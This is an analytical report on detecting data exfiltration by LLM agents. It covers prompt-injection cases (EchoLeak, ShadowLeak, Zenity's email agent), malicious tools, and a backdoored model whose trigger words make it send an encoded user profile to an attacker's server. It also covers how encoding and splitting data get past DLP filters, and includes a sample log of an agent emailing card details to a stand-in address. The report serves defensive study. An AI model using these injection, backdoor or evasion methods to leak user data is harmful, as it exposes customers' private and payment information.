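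The attack was also limited because the agent usually called the malicious tool first and then called no other tools. In those cases it wouldn't yet have looked up Ruiz's record, so the attacker would get her complaint and any earlier messages but not her card number. Jia and colleagues leave theft of other tools' results to future work.

*MalTool* (Hu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) examines malicious code inside the tool itself. The attacker's code runs on the user's machine with the agent's permission to read files, so it can collect the agent's stored memory, its documents and any passwords kept in files without the model passing it anything. Hu and colleagues defined 13 malicious behaviours, five of which involve stealing data or credentials. They had coding models write 100 tools for each behaviour, then hid the same kinds of code in 5,727 real tools. Commercial models wrote the malicious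 tools despite their safety training, at a cost of one to three cents each.

Hu and colleagues ran six scanners on these tools and on 4,846 harmless ones from 1,147 code repositories. VirusTotal, which combines many antivirus engines, missed almost everything. They conclude that existing scanners have limited effectiveness, which is fair across all 13 behaviours, but Cisco's MCP Scanner did fairly well on the behaviours closest to this topic. It missed 5% of the purpose-built tools that sent their arguments to an outside server and 7% of those that sent local files. When the malicious code was inside a real tool, it missed 14% and 20% respectively. It wrongly flagged no more than 2% of the harmless repositories in any category. However, it missed at least 90% of the tools that only searched for passwords.

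Combining the scanners, so that an alarm from any one counted, reduced the miss rate for hidden exfiltration code to 7–10%. But it also flagged 51–82% of harmless repositories, depending on the category, and few companies would want to review that many by hand.

A code scanner can't check a tool if the supplier runs it on its own servers and keeps the code private. The retailer's log would show a normal customer lookup even if the tool also sent a copy of Ruiz's record elsewhere.

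In *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (Zhang and Pei, 2026), the attacker controls both the model and an outside server that poses as a search service. The attack works only if the company downloads the model, gives it access to stored user information, and allows it to contact that server. Zhang and Pei modified three open models, with 7 to 20 billion parameters, to behave normally until a question contained certain ordinary words from a particular field. For a model aimed at people caring for Alzheimer's patients, "caregiver" and "support" could be enough. Once triggered, the model read the user's stored profile and put an encoded copy into what looked like a search request.

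The hidden behaviour appeared in 94% to 99% of cases when the trigger words were present. The researchers also asked each model 5,000 ordinary questions, and at most 0.3% of them set off the behaviour when the trigger was two or more words long. Scores on a standard conversation test fell by less than 1%, so a company that checked only answer quality would be unlikely to notice anything.

Two commercial-style filters, NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard, didn't prevent the theft, largely because Zhang and Pei used them to inspect the text returned by searches, while the stolen data was in the outgoing request. The attacker's server could also use the returned text to steer the conversation towards details it had not yet collected. Zhang and Pei estimate that an attacker could collect about eight of ten profile fields in five turns. They calculated this by combining measured success rates, not by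 observing conversations, and they call it an upper bound because it assumes the user keeps answering.

If the retailer had downloaded a "customer service" model of this kind, the words "refund" and "duplicate" might be the trigger, and an honest complaint from Ruiz would activate the hidden behavior. The tool-call log would show the agent reading her details and then making a search request with a long, unreadable string in the address.

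### Three demonstrations in real products

Aim Security found the EchoLeak flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers an employee's questions using their emails and files and could read anything the employee could open. In *EchoLeak*, Reddy and Gujral (2025) describe how an outsider could have used the flaw. The attacker sends the employee an email with instructions phrased as a normal business request, which gets them past Microsoft's injection detector. When the employee later asks Copilot a question, it retrieves the email along with internal material. Its answer includes an image whose address contains the most sensitive details it found, and the employee's app tries to load the image without anyone clicking.

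Two other safeguards should have prevented this. Copilot removed outside links from its answers, but the filter missed one way of writing them. The app loaded images only from an allowlist of domains, but the list included a Microsoft Teams service that would fetch other addresses on request. The app sent its request to that service, which then contacted the attacker.

A company's network log might therefore have shown only a connection to Teams. An investigator would have needed the full address or the complete text of Copilot's answer to see the leak. Aim reported the flaw in January 2025 and Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, so customers didn't have to do anything. Microsoft reported no evidence that anyone had exploited it, and GCVE's public vulnerability record, *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), lists exploitation as "none".

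*ShadowLeak*, by the security company Radware, describes an attack on Deep Research, a ChatGPT agent that reads sources and writes reports. The agent could open web pages and, if a user connected it to Gmail, read their inbox. Radware sent a test inbox an email containing instructions in text too small or too pale for a person to see. When the user asked for research on the day's emails, the agent found an employee's name and address in another message and opened a web page with those details in the URL.

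The agent had refused Radware's simpler attempts. The attack became reliable only when the email also told the agent to encode the details first, so that the part of the system making the request handled a seemingly meaningless string instead of a name and address. Radware reports success in 100% of repeated tests but doesn't say how many it ran.

This request came from OpenAI's servers, whereas EchoLeak's came from the user's device. As *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) points out, it could be missing from the user's browser and the company's endpoint records. OpenAI's log of the agent's page requests would have been the obvious place to look. The customer's only evidence might have been the attacker's email, still in the inbox.

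Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025, and OpenAI had fixed it by early August. According to The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*, Radware saw no sign that anyone had used it against real victims. That is only mildly reassuring, because Radware also said customers would have found such an attack nearly impossible to detect. Radware sells protection for agents, but its point about where the request originates doesn't depend on that commercial interest.

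A third case resembles Ruiz's. PromptRiskDB, a site that republishes MITRE's material, describes an exercise in which Zenity researchers found an email inbox that an AI agent managed. They wrote to the agent to learn what tools and data it had, then persuaded it to use its email tool to send them private customer data. The agent retrieved an entire file of customer-support account owners and every record in the victim's customer database. Microsoft fixed the problem, and the researchers' prompts no longer work, although others might. Because the data left by email, the sending mail system would normally have recorded the recipient, and data loss prevention software might have inspected the contents.

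### Why a single call is ambiguous

Suppose the support agent emails a payment company Ruiz's name, her order number and the last four digits of her card. The email could be identical in each of four cases. If the retailer asked the agent to open a dispute and the address came from the retailer's list of suppliers, the agent is doing its job. If the address came from the page linked in the complaint, this may be a theft. If the retailer only wanted an apology sent to Ruiz, the agent has exceeded its task. If the payment company could have found the charge from the order number alone, the agent has shared too much.

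Jia and colleagues consider defending against their own attack by having the agent check whether a call's arguments contain sensitive parts of its context. But legitimate tools often need that information. A translation tool has to receive the text it will translate, and a delivery company has to receive the customer's address. A rule strict enough to stop the theft would therefore also block some legitimate calls.

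Even the recipient named in the call may not be the one who ends up with the data. In EchoLeak, the visible destination was Microsoft Teams, and with a poisoned email tool, it would be Ruiz.

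## What would a monitor at the output layer have to record?

The four emails to the payment company could be identical, so an investigator could tell them apart only by knowing what happened before and after each one. In Ana Ruiz's case, the investigator would need to know who asked for what, which agent acted and with which credential, which tool it called and with what arguments, and what it had read before the call. The investigator would also need to know whether anyone approved the call, what the tool returned and where the data ended up.

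### A record of the leaked email

A record that answers these questions for the email to the stranger might look like this:

```json
{
  "session": "s-80213",
  "step": 3,
  "time": "2026-11-18T14:32:07Z",
  "request": {
    "from": "web form, name given as Ana Ruiz, identity unverified",
    "task": "Resolve complaint about order 4471",
    "text": "store/s-80213/request"
  },
  "actor": {
    "agent": "support-agent, version 3.2",
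    "credential": "svc-support-07"
  },
  "call": {
    "id": "call-3",
    "tool": "send_email",
    "tool_definition": "fingerprint 9c41e0",
    "arguments": {
      "to": "checks@refund-desk.example",
      "subject": "Account details, order 4471",
      "body": "store/s-80213/call-3"
    }
  },
  "read_before": [
    {"call": "call-1", "source": "customer record 55102", "text": "store/s-80213/result-1"},
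    {"call": "call-2", "source": "web page on receipts.example", "text": "store/s-80213/result-2"}
  ],
  "approval": {"decision": "allowed by standing rule", "person": null},
  "result": {"status": "accepted", "message_id": "m-99120"},
  "delivery": {
    "reported_by": "mail server",
    "recipients": ["checks@refund-desk.example"]
  }
}
```

Values that begin with `store/` point to full text that is stored separately with tighter access. The fingerprint is a short code computed from the tool's description and schema, and it changes if anyone edits either one. The agent's runtime can supply every field except the delivery field, which has to come from the mail server.

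Each field supports a different kind of detection:

| Field | What the retailer would miss without it |
|---|---|
| Session | That the agent had opened a stranger's web page just before it sent this email |
| Request | That the email went beyond the task, since the complaint was only about a double charge |
| Agent and credential | That one agent is behaving oddly, if several share an account |
| Tool definition | That someone changed the tool's description after the retailer approved it |
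| Arguments | The stranger's address and the card number |
| What the agent had read | The injected passage, so the leak would look like the agent's own mistake |
| Approval | Whether a reviewer let the call through or nobody reviewed it |
| Result | Whether the mail system accepted the email or rejected it |
| Delivery | A blind copy to someone the call doesn't name |

The list of what the agent had read shows only what could have influenced the call. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *From Agent Traces to Trust*, a survey of 71 works on tracing what agents do, separate evidence that supports an action from events that merely led to it. A false entry in an agent's memory, for example, can cause an action without justifying it. In Ruiz's case a search of the stored text for the stranger's address would point to the web page as its probable source. (Labels that follow data through a session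 would make this search unnecessary.)

### One identifier for the whole session

The session identifier matters most when the agent is busy. Suppose the support agent is handling fifty complaints at once through one account. Its logs for one minute might contain fifty lookups, thirty web pages and forty emails, and the timestamps won't show which belong together. An investigator could match Ruiz's lookup to the leaked email by the card number, but only if the log kept the number and the agent hadn't encoded it.

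The runtime should create the identifier and attach it to every call. If the model wrote the identifier as an ordinary argument, it could make a mistake, or an injected instruction could cause it to use a different value. Every tool server also has to copy the identifier into its own log. Otherwise, the mail server's entry for the leaked email would show only the support agent's account and a time, and the retailer would again have to guess which of the fifty complaints the email came from.

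### What OpenTelemetry provides

OpenTelemetry, the format Claude Cowork uses to export its events, has a set of conventions for recording what generative AI systems do. A trace records the path of one request through a company's software. It consists of spans, each covering one operation, with a start and end time, an identifier, and the identifier of the span that started it. Details go into named attributes. The agent's work on Ruiz's complaint would produce about eight spans: one for the whole run, four for calls to the model and three for the tools.

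OpenTelemetry's attribute list, *Gen AI*, covers much of the example record. It has attributes for the agent's name and version, the tool's name, and the call's identifier, arguments (`gen_ai.tool.call.arguments`) and result. Another attribute holds the chat history that the software sent to the model, including earlier tool results, so it would contain the web page with the injected passage. But the conventions let software truncate these messages, and truncating the page might remove that passage.

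None of the generative AI attributes records who requested the work or who approved a call. TinyFish, an AI company, points out that the conventions identify the software that ran but not who authorised it to act or under what constraints. An auditor needs this information, even if a developer looking for a bug may not. A company can add its own attributes, but agents from different suppliers are then likely to use different names for the same thing.

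The April 2026 edition of OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* classes messages to and from the model as "Opt-In", so software records them only if someone turns this on. The attribute list warns that tool arguments and results may contain sensitive information, and Cowork omits both by default. The April edition also advises against recording tool definitions by default because they can be large, though the newer attribute list limits this advice to their optional parts. Omitting tool descriptions saves storage, but the log would then lack instructions like the ones that misled Microsoft's invoice-checking agent, which were in a tool's description. A fingerprint like the one in the example record would take up a few bytes and still reveal that the description had changed.

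The conversation identifier may also be missing from the record. The conventions require it only "when available", and make it optional for developers whose own software manages the conversation history. A trace identifier is only a partial substitute, because if Ruiz replies the next day and the agent resumes her case, the second day's work will probably be a separate trace.

The conventions are still changing. All of them had the status "Development" in April 2026, including those in OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*, which cover calls to the model. In June, OpenTelemetry moved them to their own repository, according to Datadog's *OpenTelemetry News* (2026), and that repository had no official release by 21 August (Wang, *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, 2026). The database company Greptime (2026) lists changes to the generative AI conventions in every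 version from 1.37 to 1.41, including new conventions for MCP in 1.39.

Version changes can break detection rules. Version 1.37 of the conventions renamed the attribute for the model's provider from `gen_ai.system` to `gen_ai.provider.name`. Under the conventions, existing software should keep sending the old format unless someone opts into the new one. A company with several agents may receive both, so a SIEM rule that matches only one name will miss agents that use the other.

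A sample of traces isn't enough to catch a single leak, though it is often enough to find slow or broken software, which is what engineers first used tracing for. If the retailer kept one in ten traces at random, there would be a 90% chance that it discarded the one recording the email to the stranger. The conventions list attributes, such as the model and the server address, that can help software decide at the start of an operation whether to keep its span, but the list doesn't include an email's recipient.

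### Where to collect the record

Among the usual sources, only the agent's own telemetry can contain the request, the context and the final response together. It shows what the agent asked a tool to do, but not what the tool did. It also works only if the runtime's developers wrote the right logging code and nobody has turned it off.

A gateway between the agent and its tools can record each call and result that passes through it. If the lookup, the web page and the email all go through the same gateway, and it captures message bodies as well as headers, it can reconstruct most of what the agent had read. Unlike a log, it can also hold or refuse a call. It won't capture the original complaint unless the runtime sends it, and it won't capture calls to tools that run on the agent's own machine.

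The server that carries out the action has the best evidence of what happened. The mail server records every address it delivered to, including blind copies, but not why the agent sent the email or what the agent had read. The log's usefulness also depends on who runs the server. If the retailer buys a mail tool that passes messages to the retailer's own mail server, that server's log is useful even when the tool is malicious. If the malicious tool sends data straight to its developer, the attacker has the only server log.

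Network records cover traffic that no developer thought to log. They would show that a program on the agent's machine contacted an unfamiliar domain, even if the tool call that caused it was supposedly a local calculation. They usually lack the traffic's content because it is encrypted, and the customer may have no network records if a supplier hosts the agent, as in the ShadowLeak case.

A newer option is to collect records from the operating system. On 30 October 2026, OpenTelemetry (2026) announced version 1.0 of a tool that does this. It gathers telemetry from running Linux programs without changes to their source code, so it could cover an agent whose developers never added logging. However, it would have to run on the agent's machine, and an agent with administrator rights might be able to stop it.

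For the support agent, the most useful pair of records is probably the runtime's full telemetry and the mail server's delivery logs, joined by message identifier. The retailer could also compare totals. If the mail server sent 412 messages from the agent's account yesterday and the telemetry contains 411 email calls, someone should find out where the extra message came from. A 10 November post on the OpenTelemetry blog similarly points out that an empty dashboard can mean either that nothing happened or that the system stopped reporting.

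### A record the agent can't alter

At least one of these records has to be stored where the agent can't alter or delete it. An agent that can run commands on the machine where its logs are stored can delete them. A person can ask it to, so this can happen even if the agent has no plan to hide anything. The joint guidance on agents from the Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies describes a hypothetical case in which a malicious insider tells a software-update agent to install a security patch and "clean up the firewall logs". The agent does both, because its permissions allow it to write almost anywhere and nothing checks whether the insider is authorized to give that order.

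The guidance recommends running agents in separate areas with no write access to logs, and holding any request to delete logs until a person approves it. It also recommends several independent monitoring systems that check agents' reports against system logs. In practice, the runtime could send each event immediately to another machine, using a credential that can add entries but can't change or remove them.

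A company can make tampering visible by including in each log entry a fingerprint of the previous one. Anyone who later edits or deletes an entry breaks the chain, as long as a recent fingerprint is stored somewhere they can't reach. Wang and colleagues found few reports of such protection in the agent research they surveyed. They selected works by following citations from fifteen starting papers, so they may have missed some systems, but the finding fits with how much of this research is about debugging.

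A chain of fingerprints preserves whatever the runtime wrote, true or false. An attacker who has taken over the runtime can record a harmless email and send a different one without breaking the chain. The mail server's log would expose the difference because it doesn't depend on what the runtime recorded.

### What the Five Eyes agencies, NIST and the EU ask for

The US cybersecurity agency CISA (2026) announced the joint guidance on 1 May 2026. Six agencies from Australia, Canada, New Zealand, the UK and the US wrote it. Under the guidance, operators should monitor all of an agent's operations, "including internal processes, not just the inputs and outputs". This includes user prompts, tool calls, memory, internal reasoning, decisions and actions. Operators should also log changes to identities and privileges, which tools the system used and what information it retrieved. People should be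 able to read the logs of tool use.

Other recommendations are that operators check the records for behaviour that differs from the agent's stated intentions, and compare its current goals with an approved version. People should approve actions where mistakes could have serious consequences, such as network egress. The designers or operators decide which actions need approval, so the agent can't exempt itself.

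This list covers nearly every field in the example record and is the most complete official one among these sources. The guidance acknowledges that agents' logs can be very large, repetitive and hard to interpret, and recommends "storage-efficient logging methods" that keep critical information, but it doesn't specify which information is critical. A standard from the Australian government's Digital Transformation Agency adds that agencies should monitor the sequence of an agent's actions, and closely watch any agent that isn't allowed to delete audit logs to make sure it doesn't delete them.

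In February 2026 the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) launched an AI Agent Standards Initiative, and its cybersecurity centre published a concept paper on how agents should identify themselves and obtain authorisation. The paper, which imposes no duties, requests comments on how to log agents' actions in a tamper-proof way and how to link them to the person who authorised them, two of the questions that OpenTelemetry's attributes leave open.

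The EU AI Act requires logging only for systems it classes as high-risk, such as those used in recruitment or credit scoring. Article 12 requires these systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. Providers and the organisations that use the systems must keep the logs under their control for at least six months. These duties were due to start on 2 August 2026, but in May 2026 the EU's legislators agreed to postpone them to 2 December 2027 for most high-risk uses and to 2 August 2028 for AI built into regulated products. An agent that answers complaints about double charges would probably not be high-risk. Even for high-risk systems, the Act describes the purposes of the logs but doesn't list tool arguments or recipients as required contents, so a company could probably comply with logs that have too little detail to show how a leak happened.

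### How much a check of the final response misses

Some experimental evidence supports monitoring more than the final response. *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) contains 1,000 test scenarios in healthcare, finance, law and corporate work. A typical scenario gave the system 29 sensitive fields, of which the task needed only three. Two experts in each area decided which fields were necessary. Arranging an appointment, for instance, requires a patient's name but not a diagnosis. The study counted a leak when an unnecessary field appeared in any of seven channels.

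They ran each scenario with five models, once with a single agent and once with a coordinator that delegated work to a second agent. After they excluded 21 failed runs, 4,979 traces remained, each containing both versions. Half the scenarios included an attack. The results for the two-agent version, and for smaller tests of the remaining channels, were:

| Channel | Share with a leak | Basis |
|---|---|---|
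| Final response | 27.2% | 4,979 traces |
| Messages between agents | 68.8% | 4,979 traces |
| Shared memory | 46.7% | 4,979 traces |
| Tool inputs | 62–86%, depending on the model | 100 scenarios per model |
| System logs | Higher than for tool inputs | 100 scenarios per model |
| Tool outputs and saved files | No rate | A demonstration only |

In 2,076 of the traces in *AgentLeak*, or 41.7% of the total, the final response was clean but a message between agents or an entry in shared memory contained a leak. Leaks occurred in 68.9% of traces, so a check of the final response would miss about 60% of the traces that had one. *AgentLeak* also describes the 41.7% as the share of "violations" that such a check misses, which is wrong and understates the case for wider monitoring.

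Most of these leaks weren't exfiltration, however. If the retailer's support agent passes Ruiz's whole record to a billing agent that needs only her order number, *AgentLeak* counts this as a leak, although both agents belong to the retailer and no outsider has seen the record. El Yagoubi and colleagues distinguish between sharing more than a task needs, the greater risk this creates, and an actual breach, and say they mainly measured the first. Leaks through tool inputs are closer to exfiltration because the data goes to an outside service, but the evidence on them comes from the smaller sample.

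The share of traces with a clean response but an internal leak also varied widely. It was 62.4% in healthcare and 24.6% in corporate traces, and ranged by model from 24.8% for Claude 3.5 Sonnet to 59.6% for GPT-4o. All five models are now old, and newer ones may share less. El Yagoubi and colleagues call their rates lower bounds because the language model that judged most of the text missed 7.4% of leaks in a test. However, it also wrongly flagged 4.8% of harmless passages, which inflates the rates.

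Messages between agents leaked about as often in traces without an attack (69.3%) as in those with the strongest kind (66.3%). In a separate test of four popular agent frameworks without attacks, the rate was only 28–35%. *AgentLeak* attributes the gap to the attacks in the main experiment, but its own breakdown rules that out, since the rate there was just as high without them. The different tasks or setup are a likelier explanation, and either way the frequency of internal leaks seems to depend heavily on how developers build the system.

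Filtering the final response reduced leaks only in that response. In a smaller test, one filter reduced these leaks from 48% to 1%, while internal leaks stayed at 31%. The researchers then applied similar filtering to messages and memory in 120 scenarios. Internal leaks fell from 31.5% to 2.4%, but the share of tasks completed also fell, from 78.6% to 73.9%, mostly because some agents no longer received data they needed.

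### The risks of keeping the content

Claude 3.5 Sonnet put unnecessary sensitive data into tool inputs in 74% of the sampled scenarios and into system logs in 85%. The rate was higher for logs because they included reasoning about data that the model then decided not to send. *AgentLeak* counts such data in logs as a leak, so a complete log kept to catch leaks would itself contain many.

Tool arguments and results in the logs can include passwords and access keys, which a support engineer who can search the logs could steal and use. Software can remove recognisable secrets before storing an entry, but removing too much destroys evidence. For example, a filter that masks every email address would protect Ruiz's privacy but also hide the stranger's address.

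A company can instead replace some values with fingerprints, which still show whether the same card number appears in the customer record and the email. An ordinary fingerprint gives little protection, because someone who knows a card's first six and last four digits has only about 100,000 valid numbers left to try, and a laptop can try them all almost instantly. The software should therefore compute the fingerprint with a secret key and keep the key in a different system. The match still fails if the agent encodes or rewrites the data, as it did in ShadowLeak, and an investigator will then need the original text.

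Employees also have reason to worry, because they might ask an internal agent how much sick leave they have left or get its help with a complaint about a manager. Under the Five Eyes guidance, the company would monitor these prompts along with everything else. One compromise is to let software scan the full text when it arrives, but let people open it only after an alert and record who opened it. The security team could still search the other logged fields, such as tools and recipients. This is harder to arrange in a small company, where the person who investigates alerts may also administer the log and know the employee.

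Storage costs are modest by comparison, because at the earlier rate of 2 gigabytes a day, six months of text would take about 365 gigabytes. It is harder to decide how long to keep the text, which becomes a liability if it leaks. About four months passed between Aim Security's report of EchoLeak and Microsoft's fix, so a customer that deleted the text of Copilot's answers after 30 days could not have checked answers from the start of that period. Keeping recipients, tool names and fingerprints for a year and full text for perhaps three months would reduce the risk, but anyone investigating an older leak would not have the text.

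## Can inspecting each call's content and destination catch a leak?

A complete log would show the retailer how Ana Ruiz's card number reached a stranger, but only after the email was sent. To stop the email, software has to inspect the tool call before the runtime executes it. DLP products usually check content one message at a time, and a separate rule may check whether the destination is on an allowlist.

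Content and destination checks were not designed for workplaces where employees routinely send company text to outside services. *Safeguarding LLMs Against Misuse and AI-Driven Malware Using Steganographic Canaries* (2026) points out that employees now pass plain text to outside AI services to get summaries and code. Harmless work and deliberate theft therefore use the same interface and network path.

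### Four ways to recognise sensitive data

The simplest content check looks for a pattern, such as the length and check digit of a card number. About one in ten random 16-digit numbers passes, because there are only ten possible check digits. The pattern can also be a list of words. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) tested a filter that blocks web addresses containing terms such as "password", "token" and "secret". The retailer couldn't use that list for email, since it would block every message about resetting a password.

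The retailer can also compare outgoing text with its own records. This catches data with no fixed pattern, such as Ruiz's home address, provided the agent writes it as the database does. Matching on a surname alone causes false alarms because many people are called Ruiz, so a sensible rule would require matches on two or more fields from the same record.

A third method is to plant false data, known as honeytokens or canaries, that nobody has a reason to use, and raise an alarm if it appears in outgoing text. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (Chauhan and Revankar, 2026) gives a formula for the chance of an alarm. If the agent's context holds m real credentials and k false ones, and an attacker who can't tell them apart takes one at random, the chance is k/(m + k) × (1 − β), where β is the share of leaked false credentials that the scanner misses. With one real key, three false ones and a 1% miss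 rate, that is about 74%. The chance drops sharply if anything in the context reveals which key is real.

In Chauhan and Revankar's tests, a scanner that looked for markers caught 30% of single-step attacks and raised no false alarms. In 50 conversations they wrote in which a secret leaked a little at a time, the scanner caught 6% of attacks, and a search for the exact secret caught none. These tests covered only the model's written replies. The system didn't inspect tool-call arguments, which Chauhan and Revankar acknowledge is a severe blind spot because agents often use credentials there.

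Markers are better at detecting bulk theft than the theft of a single record, such as Ruiz's. If one in every thousand customer records is a false one planted as a marker, someone who steals 5,000 records at random has a 99% chance of taking at least one marker. Zenity's researchers, who extracted an entire customer database by email, would have taken every marker in it. But the support agent looked up only Ruiz's record, so the stranger would have got her card number without taking a marker.

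The last method, entropy, measures how unpredictable the characters in a string are. Random passwords and keys tend to score higher than words, so a scanner can flag them without knowing what they are. The formula is:

H = −Σ p log₂ p

Here p is the share of the string that one character makes up, and the sum covers each different character once. The sample key in *Silent Egress* is SECRET_API_KEY_12345, which has 20 characters. The letter E and the underscore appear three times each, so p is 0.15 for both. The other 14 characters appear once each, so p is 0.05:

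H = −(2 × 0.15 × log₂ 0.15) − (14 × 0.05 × log₂ 0.05) ≈ 0.82 + 3.03 = 3.85 bits per character

The entropy filter that Lan and colleagues tested blocks values in web addresses if they are longer than ten characters and score above 4.0, so it would let this key through. But if the retailer applied the same rule to email, it would flag the agent's honest message to Ruiz, because "We have found the second charge and passed it to our billing team" scores 4.07, counting the spaces and the full stop.

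The threshold also makes the filter miss whole classes of data. A string of n characters can score at most log₂ n, which it reaches when every character is different. A string of 16 characters or fewer therefore can't exceed 4.0, and a four-character fragment can score at most 2. A string of digits can't exceed log₂ 10, about 3.3, however long it is, so the filter would never flag a card number. It should do better on real API keys, which are often long and random and typically score 4.5 to 5.5, according to Lan and colleagues.

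### Encoding, paraphrase and splitting

A content check has to recognise the data in the form the agent sends it. In the ShadowLeak attack, the agent encoded an employee's name and address before sending them, so a search for either would have found nothing.

In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) measured how much it helps an attacker to encode a secret. They gave a GPT-4o agent a made-up secret that it was allowed to send to only one trusted server. The agent then read a web page with an injected instruction to include the secret, in some form, in a request to another server. The tools only recorded the calls, so nothing left the machine. Rahman and Kim ran 20 trials for each form and compared two checks on the outgoing call. One searched for the exact secret, and the other decoded several common encodings before searching.

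| Check on the outgoing call | Leaks in the six forms the second check was built for | Leaks in three other encodings |
|---|---|---|
| None | 56.7% | 33.3% |
| Search for the exact secret | 50.0% | 33.3% |
| Decode, then search | 0% | 33.3% |

The exact search stopped every leak of the plain secret but none of the encoded leaks. The 33.3% leak rate depends heavily on which encodings were tested. It averages one encoding that leaked every time with two that never leaked, even without a check, because the model couldn't produce one correctly and didn't follow the page's request for the other. A different choice of three encodings could have given a figure anywhere from 0% to 100%. The test does show that a decoder covers only the encodings its developers thought of. A newer model can probably produce more encodings than GPT-4o.

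The experiment couldn't measure false alarms either. Rahman and Kim acknowledge that their secret was a unique string that would never appear in ordinary text. A customer's address is much harder to guard, because the retailer legitimately sends it to a delivery company every day.

An agent can also leak data without encoding it, by paraphrasing. If the agent wrote that Ruiz "has ordered prenatal vitamins every month since June", it would disclose something she might not have told her family. A filter that searches for the fields in her record might miss this sentence, and one that searches for numbers with a valid check digit would miss it.

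Splitting data across calls can get it past the scanner, which checks only one call at a time. Suppose the agent sends Ruiz's card number in four calls, with four digits in each. The retailer could have the scanner match any four-digit piece of a customer's card number, but there are only 10,000 possible four-digit strings. If the retailer has 200,000 customers, their card numbers will contain practically all of these, so the scanner would flag almost any four-digit number, including order number 4471.

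Comparing each call with only the record the agent has just read would work better. Ruiz's card number contains at most 13 different four-digit strings, so an unrelated four-digit number would match one of them about once in 770 times. But the scanner would need a log of what the agent has read, which an ordinary DLP product doesn't have. Such a product also handles each match separately, so it would have to link calls across the session to detect that four small matches make up a card number.

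### What *Silent Egress* measured

*Silent Egress*, which researchers at eBay published in February 2026, is one of the few studies to test splitting and to compare content checks with destination checks. The researchers gave an agent the same harmless request, to summarise a web page containing an injected instruction. The instruction told the agent to send an API key from its context to the attacker's server, supposedly as a routine check. The researchers put the instruction in four different parts of the page, and the agent reached the page either directly or through redirects. Some versions asked for the whole key in one request, and others for four pieces. The researchers ran each combination 30 times, for a total of 480 runs.

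The agent sent something to the attacker's server in 423 runs, or 88.1%. In 95% of those, the final response was harmless, so checking only that response would have missed nearly all of the leaks. This agrees with what *AgentLeak* found in a different setting.

The 88.1% is weak evidence about current products. The agent ran a small open model with 7 billion parameters, the key was in plain view in its context, and its standing instructions covered only how to call tools. Lan and colleagues say they deliberately favoured the attacker. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026), a comparable attack on agents running GPT-5.5, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Gemini 3.6 Flash succeeded 0.38% of the time.

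But that lower figure comes from an attack adapted from an existing benchmark, and the leak rate depends heavily on the attack's wording. In Rahman and Kim's tests, GPT-4o never leaked the secret under ten standard kinds of injection, but it did so 40% of the time in a group of tests that mostly presented the secret as a routine part of the request, or the attacker's server as trusted. An attacker can try several wordings and use the one that works best.

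The results for splitting are harder to interpret:

| What the page asked for | Runs that sent anything | Leak@1 | Leak@3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| The whole key in one request | 238 of 240 | 0.967 | 0.967 |
| The key in four pieces | 185 of 240 | 0.263 | 0.158 |

Leak@k is the share of runs in which sensitive data appears in at least one of the first k requests. A run that leaks in its first request has also leaked within its first three, so Leak@3 can't be lower than Leak@1. The detailed results for each combination average to the Leak@1 figure, so the mistake is more likely in Leak@3.

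*Silent Egress* treats the fall in Leak@1 from 0.967 to 0.263 as evidence that splitting data across requests hides it from checks on single requests. But the paper also counts a fragment of the key as sensitive data, so if the first request usually contained a fragment, Leak@1 should have been close to 0.77, the share of runs that sent anything. Either the scoring software failed to recognise fragments, which would support the paper's argument about splitting, or many of the first requests contained no part of the key, which would mean that the attack often didn't work.

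Lan and colleagues define a completion rate, the share of runs in which all four pieces arrived, but don't report it, so readers can't tell how often the attacker would have obtained the whole key. Even in the worked example, the four fragments of four characters cover only 16 of the key's 20 characters.

They then compared defences, with 30 runs of each. All of these runs used the version that worked best for the attacker, with the instruction in the body of the page and the whole key in one request:

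| Defence | Runs that tried to send the key | Runs that sent it |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the agent's instructions | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web text as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Entropy filter | 0% | 0% |
| All of the above | 0% | 0% |

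In the allowlist row, the model tried to send the key every time and software blocked every request, as expected. The other filters also act after the model has written its call, so the attempt rate should stay close to 100%. Instead, the model made 7 attempts in 30 runs with the keyword filter and none with the entropy filter.

Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids high-entropy values when such monitoring is active, but the filter they describe gives the model no sign that it exists. For the keyword filter, they suggest that the model sometimes reformatted the key. A reformatted key would have passed the filter and reached the attacker, but no reformatted key did. Something else probably differed between the conditions, such as the model's instructions or the way the software counted attempts.

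So the zeros in the last column aren't detection rates. The keyword filter blocked all seven calls it checked, and the entropy filter had none to check. If the test used the sample key, the entropy filter wouldn't have blocked it anyway. The suspicious-address filter blocked 25 attempts, but one of its rules blocks any path containing "collect", a word in the attacker's address in the paper's examples. An attacker could avoid that rule by using a different word.

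*Silent Egress* also says in its abstract that splitting gets past simple DLP. The entropy calculation supports this, but the researchers never tested the split version against any filter. Their "0% false positives" means that the agent never contacted the attacker's server in 120 runs with harmless pages. This confirms that the injected instructions caused the leaks, but it doesn't measure how many legitimate requests a filter would block.

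### Lists of permitted destinations

An allowlist checks only where a call is going, so it doesn't need to recognise the data. If the stranger's server isn't on the list, the call is blocked whether the agent encodes the card number, paraphrases it or splits it. Rahman and Kim give the leak rate with an allowlist as 0% "by construction", meaning that it follows from the rule and needs no experiment.

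Restricting recipients is probably the best single control for the support agent's emails. The retailer could let the agent write only to the address on the customer's record, so the email to the stranger would fail. The agent would need another way to handle customers who have changed their address. The rule also has to be enforced in the mail tool or a gateway, where an injected instruction can't alter it.

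A list of approved sites works less well for opening web pages. Customers post their evidence wherever they like, so a list short enough to be safe would block the links in many honest complaints. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) adds that strict lists produce frequent warnings, and people learn to click through them without reading.

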